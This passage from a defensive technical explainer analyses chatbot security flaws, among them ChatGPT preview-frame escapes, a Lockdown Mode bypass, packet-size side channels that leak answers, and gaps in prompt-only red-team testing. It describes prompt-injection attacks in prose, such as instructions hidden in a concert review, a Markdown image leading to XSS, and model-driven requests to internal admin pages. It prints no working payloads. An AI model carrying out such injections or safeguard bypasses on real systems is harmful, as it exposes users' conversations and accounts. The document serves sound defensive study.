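Goyal describes the result as account takeover because the script could call any of ChatGPT's functions as the victim. That is a fair inference, since the script ran with ChatGPT's own origin, but the published test covered only reading and sending conversations. If ChatGPT asks for the password again before certain changes, the script could not have supplied it.

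The first working version was much less dangerous because it sent the messages from a ChatGPT App, an add-on that the victim would have had to connect or invoke. The researchers next tried an HTML attachment, which ChatGPT opened in the same kind of preview. But when they shared that conversation publicly, the link kept the attachment but not the graph, so MathLive never loaded and nothing received the messages. Finally, they put a graph and a model-written HTML page into one ordinary conversation, and the public link preserved both.

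Goyal reports two forms of this final version. In the more reliable one, the victim opened the link and clicked ChatGPT's Preview button once. In the other, the victim only had to open the link, because the researchers had marked the HTML so that ChatGPT opened the preview automatically. They reproduced the automatic form three times in a separate account, with the script running after about 4.5 seconds. These successes show that the attack could work without a click, but not how often it would. The graph and the preview loaded independently, so the preview could have sent its messages before MathLive was ready.

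According to 송, Parameter confirmed the flaw in ChatGPT's live code on 13 October and reported it on 18 October. OpenAI raised the flaw's rating from P2 to P1 on 21 October and paid a $5,000 reward. The Hacker News' *A Shared ChatGPT Link Could Run Attacker Code in Your Session* (2026) describes P1 as OpenAI's most serious category. By 26 October, both versions of ChatGPT's front end then in use rejected the messages. Parameter reported no real-world attacks.

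The attacker prepared the conversation in their own account and shared it, and the attack ran in the victim's browser when the victim opened it. Because the conversation was already complete by then, the attack did not depend on the transport that delivered the answer. It also did not require the victim's model to follow hostile instructions.

### A window outside Lockdown Mode

The second attack targeted ChatGPT's Lockdown Mode, an optional setting for people who handle sensitive data. OpenAI announced it for enterprise plans on 13 February and extended it to personal accounts from 4 June (*Introducing Lockdown Mode and Elevated Risk labels in ChatGPT*, 2026).

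ChatGPT's Lockdown Mode is meant to stop a model that follows hostile instructions from sending the user's data anywhere. It does not prevent prompt injection itself. The Next Web's *OpenAI adds Lockdown Mode to ChatGPT to block data theft* lists live browsing, images from the web, Deep Research, Agent Mode and file downloads among the features the mode disables. The mode also cuts off network access for code in Canvas, ChatGPT's editing area.

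Willison (2026) considered it crucial that these restrictions are fixed rules, because an attacker might also fool a second AI system that judged each request. Willison also inferred from the mode's existence that ChatGPT's default settings do not robustly prevent such leaks.

Brinsa (2026) points out in *ChatGPT Locked the Doors and Left a Window Open* that OpenAI's list of restricted features did not include HTML previews. The previews had arrived in February 2026, the same month as Lockdown Mode, and had their own protection. ChatGPT ran each preview inside two nested sandboxed frames and asked the user before letting the page load anything from outside or open a window.

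On 5 November 2026, the security company Check Point published a way around this, found by its researcher Alexey Bukhteyev. *Check Point Bypassed ChatGPT's Lockdown Mode With a Popup* (Duggan, 2026) explains that the sandbox had both popup permissions, so the browser itself would let a preview open a window outside the sandbox. To prevent this, ChatGPT relied on a script that replaced the browser's window-opening function, window.open, with one that asked for approval.

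However, a browser gives every frame its own copy of the built-in functions. A hostile preview could create another frame inside itself and use that frame's window.open, which ChatGPT had not replaced. The new window had no sandbox, and Lockdown Mode's restrictions did not apply to it. Opening a window sends a request to its address, so the preview could leak text from the chat by putting it in that address, much as an attacker can with an image.

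### How much did the victim have to do?

The conditions depended on the application:

| Where the victim used ChatGPT | To open the window | To download a malicious file |
|---|---|---|
| ChatGPT Classic on a desktop computer | No click | A click on a link in the window |
| A web browser | One click inside the preview | No further click |

In *Même avec son mode de verrouillage activé, ChatGPT laissait fuiter des conversations*, Loupia (2026) describes ChatGPT Classic as the former desktop application. It is built on Electron, a framework that packages web pages as desktop software. Electron let the preview open a window that the user hadn't asked for, which browsers normally block.

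Check Point demonstrated the desktop version with a malicious GPT, a customised version of ChatGPT that anyone can set up and share. As the victim chatted with it, the GPT sent their messages to the researchers' server. Check Point calls this a "zero-click" attack. The victim approved nothing, but did have to choose the malicious GPT and type something worth stealing. The attack could also start from a hostile prompt or a shared chat.

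TechRadar's *AI security controls are only as strong as the wider application environment* states in its headline that the researchers gained access to the "entire chat history". This probably means the conversation in progress. The sandbox still kept the preview from accessing ChatGPT's cookies and stored data, so the GPT's instructions most likely made the model copy the user's messages into the HTML it wrote, and the model could copy only what it had received.

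The attacker also controlled the content of the new window, which kept ChatGPT's icon in the desktop application. Check Point used this window to show a fake ChatGPT update that linked to a malicious file. In another demonstration, the researchers reloaded the application's main window and signed the user out, so that an attacker could then show a fake login page.

OpenAI told Check Point on 18 September that it had removed both popup permissions from the outer preview frame. Check Point retested and found that the technique no longer worked. OpenAI made the change on its servers, so users did not have to install anything. Antipov notes in *У ChatGPT нашли выход из режима изоляции* (2026) that the researchers reported no real attacks.

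### Getting in and getting out

Check Point told The Hacker News that its finding and Parameter's were different vulnerabilities in the same component (*Researchers Bypass ChatGPT Lockdown Mode to Exfiltrate Chats Without User Interaction*, 2026). Parameter's script crossed into the signed-in page and could request any saved conversation. Check Point's script never entered that page and only needed a way to send out data the preview already contained.

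OpenAI had already removed the popup permissions when Parameter confirmed a separate flaw in October. That repair did not cover Parameter's attack, because the attack sent messages without opening any windows.

| Repair | Parameter's attack | Check Point's attack |
|---|---|---|
| Check who sent each message | Stopped | Not stopped, because it did not rely on messages to the main page |
| Withhold both popup permissions | Not stopped | Stopped |
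| Remove YouTube from the permitted script sources | Script blocked, but the attacker could still put HTML in the page | Not stopped, because the main page's list of scripts does not govern a new window |

A server-side code sandbox can also have the second kind of flaw. In March 2026, Check Point Research's *ChatGPT Data Leakage via a Hidden Outbound Channel* described a hidden path to the internet from the isolated environment where ChatGPT runs code for users.

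### Checking who sent a message

The developers of chat.example could write a careful listener for the preview's height and still have Parameter's problem, because a library may add a careless listener of its own. One solution is to install a guard before any library loads:

```
on message(sender, message):
    if the sender is the main page itself:
        let the other listeners receive the message
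    otherwise:
        stop the message from reaching any other listener
        if the sender is the preview frame and the message
        contains only a height from 50 to 2,000 pixels:
            resize the preview
```

The guard checks which window sent a message rather than the message's origin, because sandboxed frames usually all have the origin "null", including any that a hostile page creates. If chat.example embeds another service that needs to send messages, such as a payment form, the developers have to add that service's frame and its permitted messages to the guard.

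The risk also depends on the message format. A height is a number and can't carry a script, but MathLive's keyboard layout could contain any HTML. Even a trusted sender should not need to send HTML to the main page, because an attacker who compromises that sender could send it too.

The developers could also run the graph in its own sandboxed frame. A hostile preview might still send a message to MathLive there, but the resulting HTML would appear in a frame without access to the user's account. This uses some memory and makes the layout harder to manage, but it protects the main page from undiscovered flaws in the graph library.

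### Closing the ways out

Replacing window.open failed because ChatGPT had to replace it in every frame, including frames that the hostile page created later. A sandbox restriction on the outer frame is more reliable because the browser applies it to every frame nested inside, and none of them can lift it. The replaced function can still show the user an explanation, but it should not be the only defense.

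If previews have to keep data in, chat.example must block more than new windows:

| Way out | How to close it |
|---|---|
| Requests, images and WebSockets | Give the preview page a CSP that permits no outside addresses |
| Loading another page in the preview's own frame | List only the preview's address in the main page's rule for frames |
| New windows | Withhold both popup permissions from the outer frame |

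The strict policy can break generated pages, because they often load a chart or game library from a public host. Allowing the whole host is risky, since some of these hosts serve files that anyone can publish. It is safer to keep copies of the most popular libraries on the preview's own origin and tell the model to use those.

An approval dialog is a weaker alternative. It lets a page fetch the weather, for example, but the user has to notice if the address also contains a line from their conversation. A mode advertised as keeping data in should refuse the request instead of asking the user.

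### Script sources that anyone can use

Allowing YouTube in ChatGPT's policy caused trouble for the same reason as allowing Bing in Copilot's. Both companies trusted an entire host, and an attacker could exploit one address on that host.

chat.example can avoid this by showing YouTube videos in a frame. The policy then has to permit YouTube only as a source of frames, so a YouTube script can't run in the chatbot's page. If the page really needs a script from another company, the developers can host a reviewed copy.

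They can also use a nonce, a random value that the server generates for each page load and attaches to its own script tags. With a policy based only on nonces, the browser runs a script tag only if it has the right value, wherever the script comes from. An attacker who can insert HTML but not yet run a script has no practical way to learn the value.

The Hacker News reports that Parameter considered YouTube the last step, not the cause. Blocking YouTube would still have let the preview insert HTML into the main page. An attacker could then have shown a fake login form under ChatGPT's real address, even without running a script. The sender check is therefore the main fix, and the stricter policy limits the damage if another listener handles messages unsafely.

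### Harm without an escape

Attackers have already used generated pages for phishing without needing either flaw. According to Infosecurity Magazine's *Attackers Abuse Shared Content for ChatGPT Phishing Campaign*, the security company Push Security found pages that criminals had built with ChatGPT's code-rendering feature. The pages imitated ChatGPT's brand, appeared on genuine ChatGPT domains and sent visitors to a fake download page with a malicious program.

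Even a perfect sandbox would not stop a person from believing what such a page displays. chat.example can make the deception harder by putting a permanent label above every shared preview, outside the frame, stating that another user made the page. It can also require a click before a shared preview opens. The click would not have stopped the more reliable form of Parameter's attack, but it gives the visitor a chance to read the label before the page can imitate anything.

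## What does the encrypted stream reveal to someone watching the network?

Someone who can watch the traffic between a user and chat.example can learn something about an answer without attacking the page or the server. TLS, the protocol behind https addresses and encrypted WebSockets, encrypts the text so they can't read it, but it doesn't hide the size or arrival time of each message. In a streamed answer, the size of each message depends on the words in it.

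The watcher could be a stranger on the same café Wi-Fi, an employer that runs the office network, an internet provider or a government with access to the provider's equipment. A hostile web page can't watch the network because its scripts can't read other sites' packets, the small units in which a network carries data.

Origin checks and sanitizers don't affect this flaw because it is in the transport, not the web page. It applies to both SSE and WebSockets, which normally run over TLS and differ here only in how many bytes they add around each piece of text.

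### From packet sizes to word lengths

Suppose chat.example sends the sentence "You should see a doctor today." one text token at a time. Its message format adds 41 bytes to each token, the WebSocket header adds 2, and a common form of TLS adds 22, which makes a fixed overhead of 65 bytes:

| Text token | Length, with any leading space | Size on the network |
|---|---|---|
| "You" | 3 | 68 |
| " should" | 7 | 72 |
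| " see" | 4 | 69 |
| " a" | 2 | 67 |
| " doctor" | 7 | 72 |
| " today" | 6 | 71 |
| "." | 1 | 66 |

The watcher sees only the last column. Subtracting the overhead of 65 from each size gives the token lengths: 3, 7, 4, 2, 7, 6, 1. They can find the overhead by opening their own account and looking at its traffic, or by assuming that the smallest message contains a single character. If the server sends the whole answer so far every time, as Open WebUI once did, they subtract each size from the next one instead.

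A watcher can't identify the words from their lengths alone, because "You should see a doctor today." and "You should see a lawyer today." produce exactly the same sizes. In *What Was Your Prompt?*, Weiss, Ayzenshteyn and colleagues (2024) give the example of a sentence missing two nouns, of four and five letters, which English speakers could complete in nearly 800,000 ways. The watcher therefore needs some way to pick the likely ones.

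### Rebuilding the answer

Weiss and colleagues trained language models to translate lists of token lengths into English. The task was easier because chatbots open many answers with stock phrases. The researchers trained one model on the opening sentences of GPT-4's answers and another on the later sentences. The second model also received the reconstruction of the previous sentence as a clue.

In the published study, Weiss and colleagues report that their attack accurately reconstructed 27% of answers and inferred the topic of 53%. An earlier version of the study gives nearly the same figures and shows that they cover only the opening segment of each answer, roughly one sentence. For whole answers, the attack inferred the topic in 38% of cases and came very close to the text in 5%.

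The test for a correct topic was also generous. A reconstruction passed if it scored above 0.5 on a standard measure of similarity in meaning. One reconstruction scored 0.66 even though it was about alcohol's effect on sleep and the original sentence was about its effect on the liver, a difference that could matter a great deal to the person who asked.

The attack also worked on real traffic. It inferred the topic of the opening segment for 38% of answers from ChatGPT's web page and 41% from Microsoft's Copilot when the services sent tokens one at a time. OpenAI's developer API sent tokens in pairs, which reduced the figure to 18%. ChatGPT used HTTP over QUIC, a newer transport protocol, while many other services used WebSockets.

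These results are now mostly out of date. Cloudflare, which hosts models for developers, added random padding in March 2024. *NetEcho* (Zhang, Wu and colleagues, 2025) reports that by October 2025, OpenAI, Anthropic and Google were grouping and padding the output of their own chatbots. DeepSeek's chatbot still sent each token separately.

### Guessing only the topic

Someone watching the network may be able to identify the topic of a conversation without decrypting it. In *Whisper Leak* (2025), McDonald and Bar Or, both at Microsoft, tested whether they could recognise conversations about one chosen topic from the sizes and timing of the packets. They wrote 100 versions of a question about whether money laundering is legal and sent each one 100 times to 28 models. They mixed in 11,716 unrelated questions from Quora, trained classifiers to tell the two groups apart, and tested them on versions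 of the question that the classifiers had not seen.

The best classifier scored above 97% on 17 of the 28 models. The score combines recall, the share of money-laundering conversations that the classifier catches, and precision, the share of flagged conversations that are about money laundering.

Grouping tokens did not reliably prevent this. The classifier still scored 99% on Alibaba's Qwen models (about four tokens per group), 91% on Anthropic's Claude 3 Haiku (six), and 84% on Google's Gemini 2.5 Pro (about 18). Grouping hides the length of each word, but the sequence of group sizes and pauses still differs between answers.

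The experiment covered only one topic and used single questions. Many of the Quora questions, such as where in the world most rainbows occur, were also very different from the target topic. Telling money laundering from tax law would probably be harder.

### When the topic is rare

Nearly half the conversations in the experiment were about money laundering, but almost none would be on a real network, so even a low rate of false alarms matters. McDonald and Bar Or therefore projected their results to a network with 10,000 other conversations for each one about money laundering.

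Suppose an internet provider watches a million ordinary conversations and 100 about money laundering, and its classifier catches half of the 100. The precision depends on how often the classifier wrongly flags an ordinary conversation:

| False alarms in a test with 2,343 ordinary questions | False alarms in a million conversations | Correct flags | Precision |
|---|---|---|---|
| 0 | 0 | 50 | 100% |
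| 1 | 427 | 50 | 10.5% |
| 4 | 1,707 | 50 | 2.8% |

McDonald and Bar Or do not state how many Quora questions they used in the test, but their results fit 2,343, a fifth of the total. With that many questions, a single false alarm would lower the projected precision at 50% recall from 100% to 10.5%. At that recall, they report a precision of exactly 10.5% for four models and 100% for eight others.

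The 100% figures therefore probably mean that the classifier raised no false alarms on about 2,300 questions, which is too few to show that the false-alarm rate is below 1 in 10,000. If the true rate were 1 in 2,343, a test of this size would produce no false alarms 37% of the time. McDonald and Bar Or themselves advise reading the projections conservatively.

A precision of 10.5% can still be useful to a government. It would have 477 flagged conversations to examine instead of a million, and about one in ten would be on the topic, compared with one in 10,000 before. People in the other 427 conversations might come under suspicion for asking about something else. A watcher could be more accurate by waiting until the same person triggers several flags, although someone who often asks about banking law might trigger repeated false alarms.

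### How much the defences help

McDonald and Bar Or began telling providers about the leak in June 2025. OpenAI and xAI introduced defences in August, Mistral in September and Microsoft in October. Other providers declined or never replied. iTnews' *AI providers plug metadata leak that exposed encrypted chat topics* reports no sign that anyone had used the attack, but this is weak reassurance because passively recording traffic leaves no trace on the server.

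Providers can use three main defences. They can add random filler to each message, send several tokens together, or inject fake messages between the real ones. Wei, Abdulrazzag and colleagues (2024), in *When Speculation Spills Secrets*, also measured padding and grouping, against an attack that identified which of 50 medical questions a user had asked. The results of the two studies are not directly comparable:

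| Defence | Study | Effect on the attack | Cost |
|---|---|---|---|
| Random padding | McDonald and Bar Or | Score fell from 97.5% to 92.9% | Extra data, not measured |
| Random padding | Wei and colleagues | Accuracy fell by 70% | Up to 8.7 times the payload |
| Groups of five tokens | McDonald and Bar Or | Score fell from 98.2% to 94.8% | Text appears in small jumps |
| Grouping | Wei and colleagues | Accuracy fell by up to 50% | No larger payload, but some delay |
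| Injected packets | McDonald and Bar Or | Score fell from 98.1% to 93.3% | Usually 2 to 3 times the traffic |
| Padding to a fixed size | Wei and colleagues | Accuracy fell by 98% | 230 times the payload |

McDonald and Bar Or's rows all cover GPT-4o mini, which they chose because the defences worked unusually poorly on it. For most of the models they tested, sending tokens in groups of five or more removed most of the risk. But they simulated this grouping on recorded traffic, and the results for Qwen show that a provider's real grouping can protect much less.

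A score of 93% also overstates the risk when the topic is rare. The attack on Microsoft's copy of GPT-4o mini scored 93.4% in the main experiment, without any defence, but its precision was only 2.3% at 10% recall in the projection for a rare topic. This low precision supports McDonald and Bar Or's view that random padding probably removes the practical risk from current attacks, though they expect attacks to improve.

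Padding works less well if the server uses speculative decoding, a technique in which it guesses several tokens ahead and keeps the correct ones. Tokens then arrive in larger groups when the text is predictable than when it is difficult, so the traffic pattern depends on the text. Padding each token doesn't hide how many arrive together.

Zhang and colleagues trained a classifier to choose among ten medical or ten legal topics. When it had only the number of tokens in each group, which is roughly what padding leaves visible, it was right about 11% of the time for a chatbot based on GPT-4o, almost the same as guessing. For DeepSeek's chatbot, which generates several tokens at once, it was right 73% of the time on medical topics and 55% on legal ones.

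Fake packets must be numerous to hide a conversation's topic. In Zhang and colleagues' simulations of DeepSeek's API, the classifier identified 94% of legal topics when there were 20% as many fake packets as real ones. That fell to 24% with half as many fake packets as real ones, and to 12% with equal numbers.

### Work from 2026

Pouryousef, Lopez and colleagues (2026), in *A Large-Scale Benchmark and Risk Assessment of Traffic Analysis Attacks*, recorded 60,000 interactions with ten open models over SSE. They used 60 prompts in six categories, such as summarising, programming and logical puzzles. A classifier given only the response traffic chose the right category 67% of the time, compared with 17% for guessing.

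Accuracy fell only to 59% when the researchers removed every feature based on packet size, and to 60% when they removed timing instead. A defence that hides just one of the two may therefore leave most of the leak. But the researchers did not test padded traffic, and ten prompts per category is a small sample of what people ask.

An observer could also identify the category from the size of the encrypted request alone 52% of the time, because people tend to paste long texts when they want a summary and write short prompts for a puzzle. Padding only the chatbot's answers does not hide the request's size.

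An attacker can also make the traffic easier to recognise. *SkillWatermark* (2026) describes how an attacker could publish a skill (saved instructions for a model) with planted wording that produces a distinctive traffic pattern, then look for that pattern on the network. The patterns were consistent across 14 subject areas, and auditing tools based on language models did not flag the altered skills as malicious.

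### The developer's own connection

chat.example can leak even if its model provider pads every message. The padding protects the connection between the provider and chat.example's server. The server removes it, reads the text and opens a new message for each piece it sends to the browser. If the server splits the provider's groups into single tokens, the user's connection reveals more than the provider's did.

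Zhang and colleagues built a chatbot on GPT-4o with the web framework Next.js to measure what the encrypted stream reveals. Their classifier identified 73% of medical topics from the connection between GPT-4o's API and its customer, and 92% from the connection between the chatbot and the user.

They also tried to recover whole conversations and report an average success rate of 95%, but they again counted a similarity of only 0.5 as success. The medical prompts all followed a similar form, and the sample prompts that the attack retrieved as a starting point already had a similarity of 0.94 to the victim's. The high rate is therefore weak evidence of how much private detail the attack recovered, and the topic results are better evidence of what the encrypted stream reveals.

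McDonald and Bar Or describe messages of uniform size at a fixed rate as strong protection, though expensive. Grouping the tokens first makes it much cheaper. The server at chat.example could do this:

```
every 0.1 seconds, while an answer is in progress:
    take the text that has arrived, up to 190 bytes
    keep any remaining text for the next message
    add filler until the encrypted message is 256 bytes long
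    send it, even if it contains no new text
```

At 50 tokens per second, a 3,000-token answer takes a minute to arrive. With four characters per token, sending each token separately uses 3,000 × 69 bytes, or about 207 kilobytes, most of it overhead. The padded version uses 600 × 256 bytes, or about 154 kilobytes, but the reader waits up to a tenth of a second longer for each word. The developers also have to turn off compression on the connection or use random filler, because compression would shrink filler made of repeated characters and expose the length again.

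The watcher could still see how long the model took to start and how long it wrote. In Pouryousef and colleagues' tests, the total amount of response traffic was enough to identify the category 37% of the time. To hide some of this, chat.example could keep sending filler until the next multiple of 15 seconds. It could hide all of the streaming pattern by sending the finished answer at once, but users would then face the wait that streaming was meant to avoid.

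## Why do tests of the model miss these flaws, and what finds them?

Most tests of a language model send prompts and grade the text that comes back, without opening the chatbot's page. They can show that a model will write something harmful, but not whether a server checks the Origin header or whether a page runs the model's text as a script.

### What a prompt test covers

A typical test has four steps:

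1. A program takes a prompt from a prepared set, such as a request for the model's hidden instructions.
2. It may rewrite the prompt, perhaps in base64 or another language, to get around the model's training.
3. It sends the prompt to the model's API and receives the reply as text.
4. A grader, often another language model, decides whether the attack worked.

Microsoft's open-source tool PyRIT has components for each step, according to *Lessons From Red Teaming 100 Generative AI Products* (Bullwinkel, Minnich and colleagues, 2025). A model can answer the same prompt differently each time, so testers repeat their attacks, and automation lets them do this quickly. *Redefining AI Red Teaming in the Agentic Era* (2026) describes a run of 674 attacks on Llama Scout, a Meta model. The run included 7,727 trials and took about three hours, and about 85% of the attacks succeeded.

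Those trials tested a model, so even ten times as many would not have found a fault in a website. A prompt test of this kind leaves out:

- The browser: the grader reads the reply as text, and no front end turns it into a page.
- The Origin header: the program logs in with an API key, so the test never shows what the server would do if a hostile website asked to connect.
- A second user: nobody else opens the transcript or tries to read it without permission.
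- A logout: the test ends without checking whether an old login still works.
- The network: the program receives decrypted text, so the grader can't see the packet sizes.

Better grading would not close these gaps, because a grader who sees only the model's reply can't tell what the front end will do with it. If the reply ends with an HTML image that has an event handler, one front end may display the tag as text and another may run the handler.

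*A Systematic Review of Algorithmic Red Teaming Methodologies for Assurance and Security* (2026) recommends judging an AI agent over a whole series of interactions instead of one reply at a time. This would help testers notice a harmful tool call in the middle of a task, but they would still need a browser to find a rendering flaw.

### Five tests compared

Four other tests cover most of what a prompt suite leaves out. A browser rendering test feeds chosen model answers to the real front end and records every script that runs and every request that leaves the page. In a two-account test, one user tries to reach the other's data, and one of them logs out or loses a role while connected. In a proxy test, the tester intercepts, changes and resends the handshake and the messages that follow. A packet capture records the encrypted traffic as an eavesdropper on the network would see it.

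| Flaw | Prompt suite | Browser rendering | Two accounts | Proxy | Packet capture |
|---|---|---|---|---|---|
| Missing Origin check | No | No | No | Yes | No |
| Socket that outlives a logout or demotion | No | No | Yes | Yes | No |
| Access to another user's chat or session | Partly | No | Yes | Partly | No |
| Forged roles or message types | No | Partly | No | Yes | No |
| Model text that runs as script | Partly | Yes | Partly | Partly | No |
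| Data leak through an image | Partly | Yes | No | Partly | Partly |
| Preview that escapes its frame | No | Yes | No | No | No |
| Packet sizes that reveal words | No | No | No | Partly | Yes |

"Partly" means the test can find some cases or give the tester a reason to look further. For example, a packet capture may show the browser contacting an unexpected server, but not what it sent.

A "Yes" also depends on how carefully the testers work. A rendering test that inspects only the finished page will miss an image that appeared for a tenth of a second during the stream. A proxy test of the company's servers will miss an assistant such as OpenClaw, whose gateway runs on the user's computer.

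### Flaws outside the agreed scope

Testers can also miss a flaw because their client did not ask them to look there. SpiderLabs spent several days on the loan application and found only minor problems before noticing a small chat box in the same colour as the page. According to LevelBlue, the chatbot ran on one domain and exchanged data with another, both outside the agreed scope. A tester who kept strictly to that scope would have missed the chatbot, which was the most dangerous part of the application.

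In July 2026, three researchers from the security company Hacktron reached the ChatGPT accounts of several OpenAI employees through OpenAI's help forum. *Hacking OpenAI* (rootxharsh, s1r1us and iamnoooob, 2026) explains that the forum used an outdated image library that let an uploaded picture run code on the forum's server. A separate fault in OpenAI's login system then let the researchers move from the forum to ChatGPT. One employee's account gave them access to OpenAI's internal code, where they proposed a harmless change to prove they had access.

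OpenAI fixed the fault in its own system about 14 hours after the report and paid $6,500. It said the reward was only for that fault and that its bug bounty explicitly excluded the forum, which runs on another company's software. A company has good reasons not to invite attacks on a supplier's servers, but this forum shared a login with ChatGPT, so an attacker could still use it.

A test can also miss a flaw on a page it covers. Escape, which sells its own tests, reports that both customer chats with the frame flaw had passed their existing checks, but it doesn't describe those checks. It explains, plausibly, that scanners don't flag rehype-raw because the plugin is working as documented.

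### What red teams find

A red team attacks a system with its owner's permission to find weaknesses. Microsoft's AI red team had examined over 100 products by October 2024, and Bullwinkel and colleagues warn that attacks aimed only at the model may not work on the finished product. Testers who ignore the input filters, databases and other ordinary software around the model will probably miss important flaws.

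One of their examples involved no prompt. A Microsoft application that processed video with generative AI used an old version of FFmpeg, a common video program. The red team uploaded a crafted playlist file, and FFmpeg made the server send requests to internal addresses that an outsider could not reach, an attack called server-side request forgery (SSRF). The developers updated FFmpeg and moved it to an isolated environment without network access.

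Microsoft's red team looked mainly for application flaws in 2021. Since then, a growing share of its work has concerned harmful content such as hate speech. Bullwinkel and colleagues still recommend testing for both. They cite a case in which encrypted streams revealed the lengths of words, a leak that did not depend on any weakness in the model.

NVIDIA's red team has assessed dozens of applications that use language models. One of its three most significant findings is that pages can leak data by rendering active content, such as images and links. Researchers had described this kind of leak by mid-2023, but the team was still finding it when it published its advice in October 2025. The team gives no count, so its advice doesn't show how common the flaw is.

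Another of NVIDIA's three findings is poor access control on the documents that a chatbot searches for its answers. A tester with one account could easily miss this, because an answer based on a colleague's private file looks normal. With two accounts, the tester can check for this by putting a made-up word in one user's file and asking about it as the other user.

### How the guidance ranks output handling

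OWASP, a non-profit foundation for software security, publishes a list of the ten main risks in applications built on language models. One entry, *LLM05:2025 Improper Output Handling*, advises developers to treat the model like any other user, validate what it sends to other parts of the system, and encode its output for the place where it will appear. The entry also recommends a strict Content Security Policy.

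This risk fell from fifth place to tenth in the 2026 edition, although its entry now also covers pages that automatically fetch outside resources named in an answer. Invicti's *OWASP LLM Top 10 2026* (2026) attributes the fall to other risks being more urgent, not to this one having decreased. A team that has time for only the first five items would now skip it.

The ranking also rests largely on opinion, since a vote among practitioners counts for three-quarters of it and 7,714 incidents from public vulnerability databases count for the rest. Prompt injection came first in the vote but would not have reached the top ten on incidents alone. OWASP says this is because companies defend against it well enough to keep most attacks out of the databases. It may also be because these databases record faults in particular software products, and when a model follows a hostile instruction there is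 often no faulty line of code to record.

Infosecurity Magazine reports that OWASP advises developers to assume someone will eventually get past the model's instructions, and to limit what the model may do and where its output may go.

Academic surveys have had a similar gap. *Shifting from Injection to Interaction* (Singh, Abuadbba and colleagues, 2026) compares 11 earlier surveys of language-model security. Six covered web applications that use such models, but none linked the models' risks to traditional web weaknesses. Singh and colleagues chose these criteria to show what their own survey adds, so it is not surprising that no earlier survey met them all.

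One survey maps nine of OWASP's ten risks from 2025 to entries in MITRE's catalogue of software weaknesses. The tenth, misinformation, has no direct equivalent there. The mapping is a useful start for a test plan, but it places XSS under prompt injection, while OWASP attributes it to poor output handling. A team that followed the mapping literally might look for XSS with prompts alone. The mapping also omits WebSockets that lack an Origin check.

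### What bug bounties pay for

Large laboratories pay outside researchers who report flaws, but they separate software flaws from misbehaviour by the model. Under its May 2026 rules, Anthropic's bug bounty covers infrastructure and code but excludes hallucinations, harmful content and jailbreaks, which are prompts that get a model to break its rules. Researchers can apply to a separate Anthropic programme for model safety.

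OpenAI (2026) also has two programmes. Its Safety Bug Bounty, launched in March, accepts prompt injections that make an agent leak a user's data or take a harmful action, if the attack works at least half the time. Reports of access beyond a user's permissions go to the older Security Bug Bounty. An earlier copy of that programme's rules excludes the content of prompts and replies unless it has a further security effect that OpenAI can verify directly.

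A prompt injection that leads to XSS involves both the model and the software. It should help that OpenAI's two teams can pass a report between them. The researcher's best evidence is a script that runs in another test account's browser, because this shows a software flaw regardless of how often the model follows the injected instructions.

Anthropic's bounty also excludes missing HttpOnly flags on cookies, denial of service, and password guessing on pages that need no login. These exclusions reduce the number of trivial reports, and researchers may still combine several weaknesses in one report if they need to show the impact. But developers won't learn from such a bounty about every small fault that an attacker could later combine with another, so they have to look for those faults themselves.

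### When a prompt leads to a web flaw

A prompt suite can still lead a tester to a serious web flaw. Quarkslab's team ran the prepared prompts from one such suite, Spikee, against a customer's medical assistant. One prompt told the model to include a Markdown image in its reply. When the testers reviewed the results, they noticed that the page had displayed the image.

They followed this up by hand:

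1. They asked the model for a frame whose address contained a script, and the page ran it. There was no adequate Content Security Policy to stop it.
2. The script could read the user's login, because the cookie had no HttpOnly flag.
3. Every conversation had a predictable address, and the server did not check who was asking for it. The attacker could therefore send a link to someone else.
4. If an administrator opened the link, the attacker received the administrator's login and could take over the platform.

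Quarkslab found these flaws in the live system but published a laboratory copy because the customer's details were confidential and the original model was no longer available. The post is therefore a better record of how the chain works than of the original product.

Spikee found the first clue, a reply containing a harmless picture. A grader that looked only for forbidden content might have passed that reply. The testers had to recognise that the picture meant the page was rendering Markdown, and then use a browser and a second account to find the rest.

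Prompts can also reveal missing permission checks if the model has access to real data. Tsigkopoulos and Ntantogian describe a public case in which a shop's chatbot gave a customer's email address to anyone who supplied an order number. Each number had a fixed prefix and six digits, so there were at most a million to try. A prompt suite could find this flaw only if it tested the shop's actual chatbot and the grader had enough information to identify the address as someone else's.

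### One application, seven models

TicketOracle, a test application by Tsigkopoulos and Ntantogian, shows how much the result of a prompt test can depend on the model. It is a concert-ticket chatbot with one tool, which fetches any web address the model gives it. Its administration pages accept connections only from the server itself, but the tool can open them, so an attacker may be able to reach them by asking the model. The researchers deliberately built in this flaw, which is the same kind as the one in Microsoft's video application.

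They tried five attacks on seven models in April 2026. In four, the attacker typed a request directly into the chat. In the fifth, the attacker hid instructions in a concert review, and an ordinary user then asked about the concert. The table gives the number of successes in ten trials:

| Model | Probe a port | Read user records | Change data | Change data, empty response | Hidden instructions in a review |
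|---|---|---|---|---|---|
| Llama 3.3 70B | 10 | 10 | 10 | 10 | 10 |
| DeepSeek R1 | 10 | 10 | 10 | 7 | 0 |
| Qwen3 Coder 480B | 9 | 10 | 10 | 7 | 0 |
| Gemini 3 Pro Preview | 0 | 7 | 10 | 0 | 0 |
| GPT-oss 120B | 3 | 0 | 10 | 0 | 0 |
| GPT-5.2 | 0 | 0 | 0 | 0 | 0 |
| Claude Opus 4.6 | 0 | 0 | 0 | 0 | 0 |

The direct attacks succeeded in 143 of 280 trials, but the main result is the difference between models. In the same application, every attack worked every time with Llama, and none worked with GPT-5.2 or Claude Opus 4.6. A company that tested the application only with GPT-5.2 might have considered it safe, then exposed its user records by switching to a cheaper model.

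These flaws are in the application, and the model affects how often an attacker reaches them. If TicketOracle's server built each address itself from a valid concert number, no model could make it open the administration pages.

Zero successes in ten trials is also weak evidence of safety. If an attack worked 10% of the time, ten independent trials would still all fail 35% of the time. These trials were not independent, because the researchers ran all ten in one conversation. Claude's refusals became shorter and firmer as they repeated the request, so an attacker who started a new conversation each time might have had different results. An attacker can also keep trying, and an attack that works 1% of the time has a 95% chance of succeeding at least once in 300 attempts.

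The results for the instructions hidden in a review come from a version with a stricter prompt, which listed the addresses the model was allowed to fetch. This prompt blocked all the direct attacks on every model. With the hidden instructions, though, successful attacks on Llama rose from six to ten, while those on GPT-oss fell from five to none. This comparison is not quite fair, because the researchers also changed the review to claim that the list now included the administration page. It still shows that a rule in the prompt does not guarantee that the model will follow it. The server would fetch any address, whether or not it was on the list.

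The researchers usually counted an attack as successful only if the chatbot also repeated the result to the user. That rule would miss an attack that made the model delete a record without mentioning it. For the attack with an empty response, they checked the server's log instead. Testers of a real chatbot should do the same for any action that changes data.

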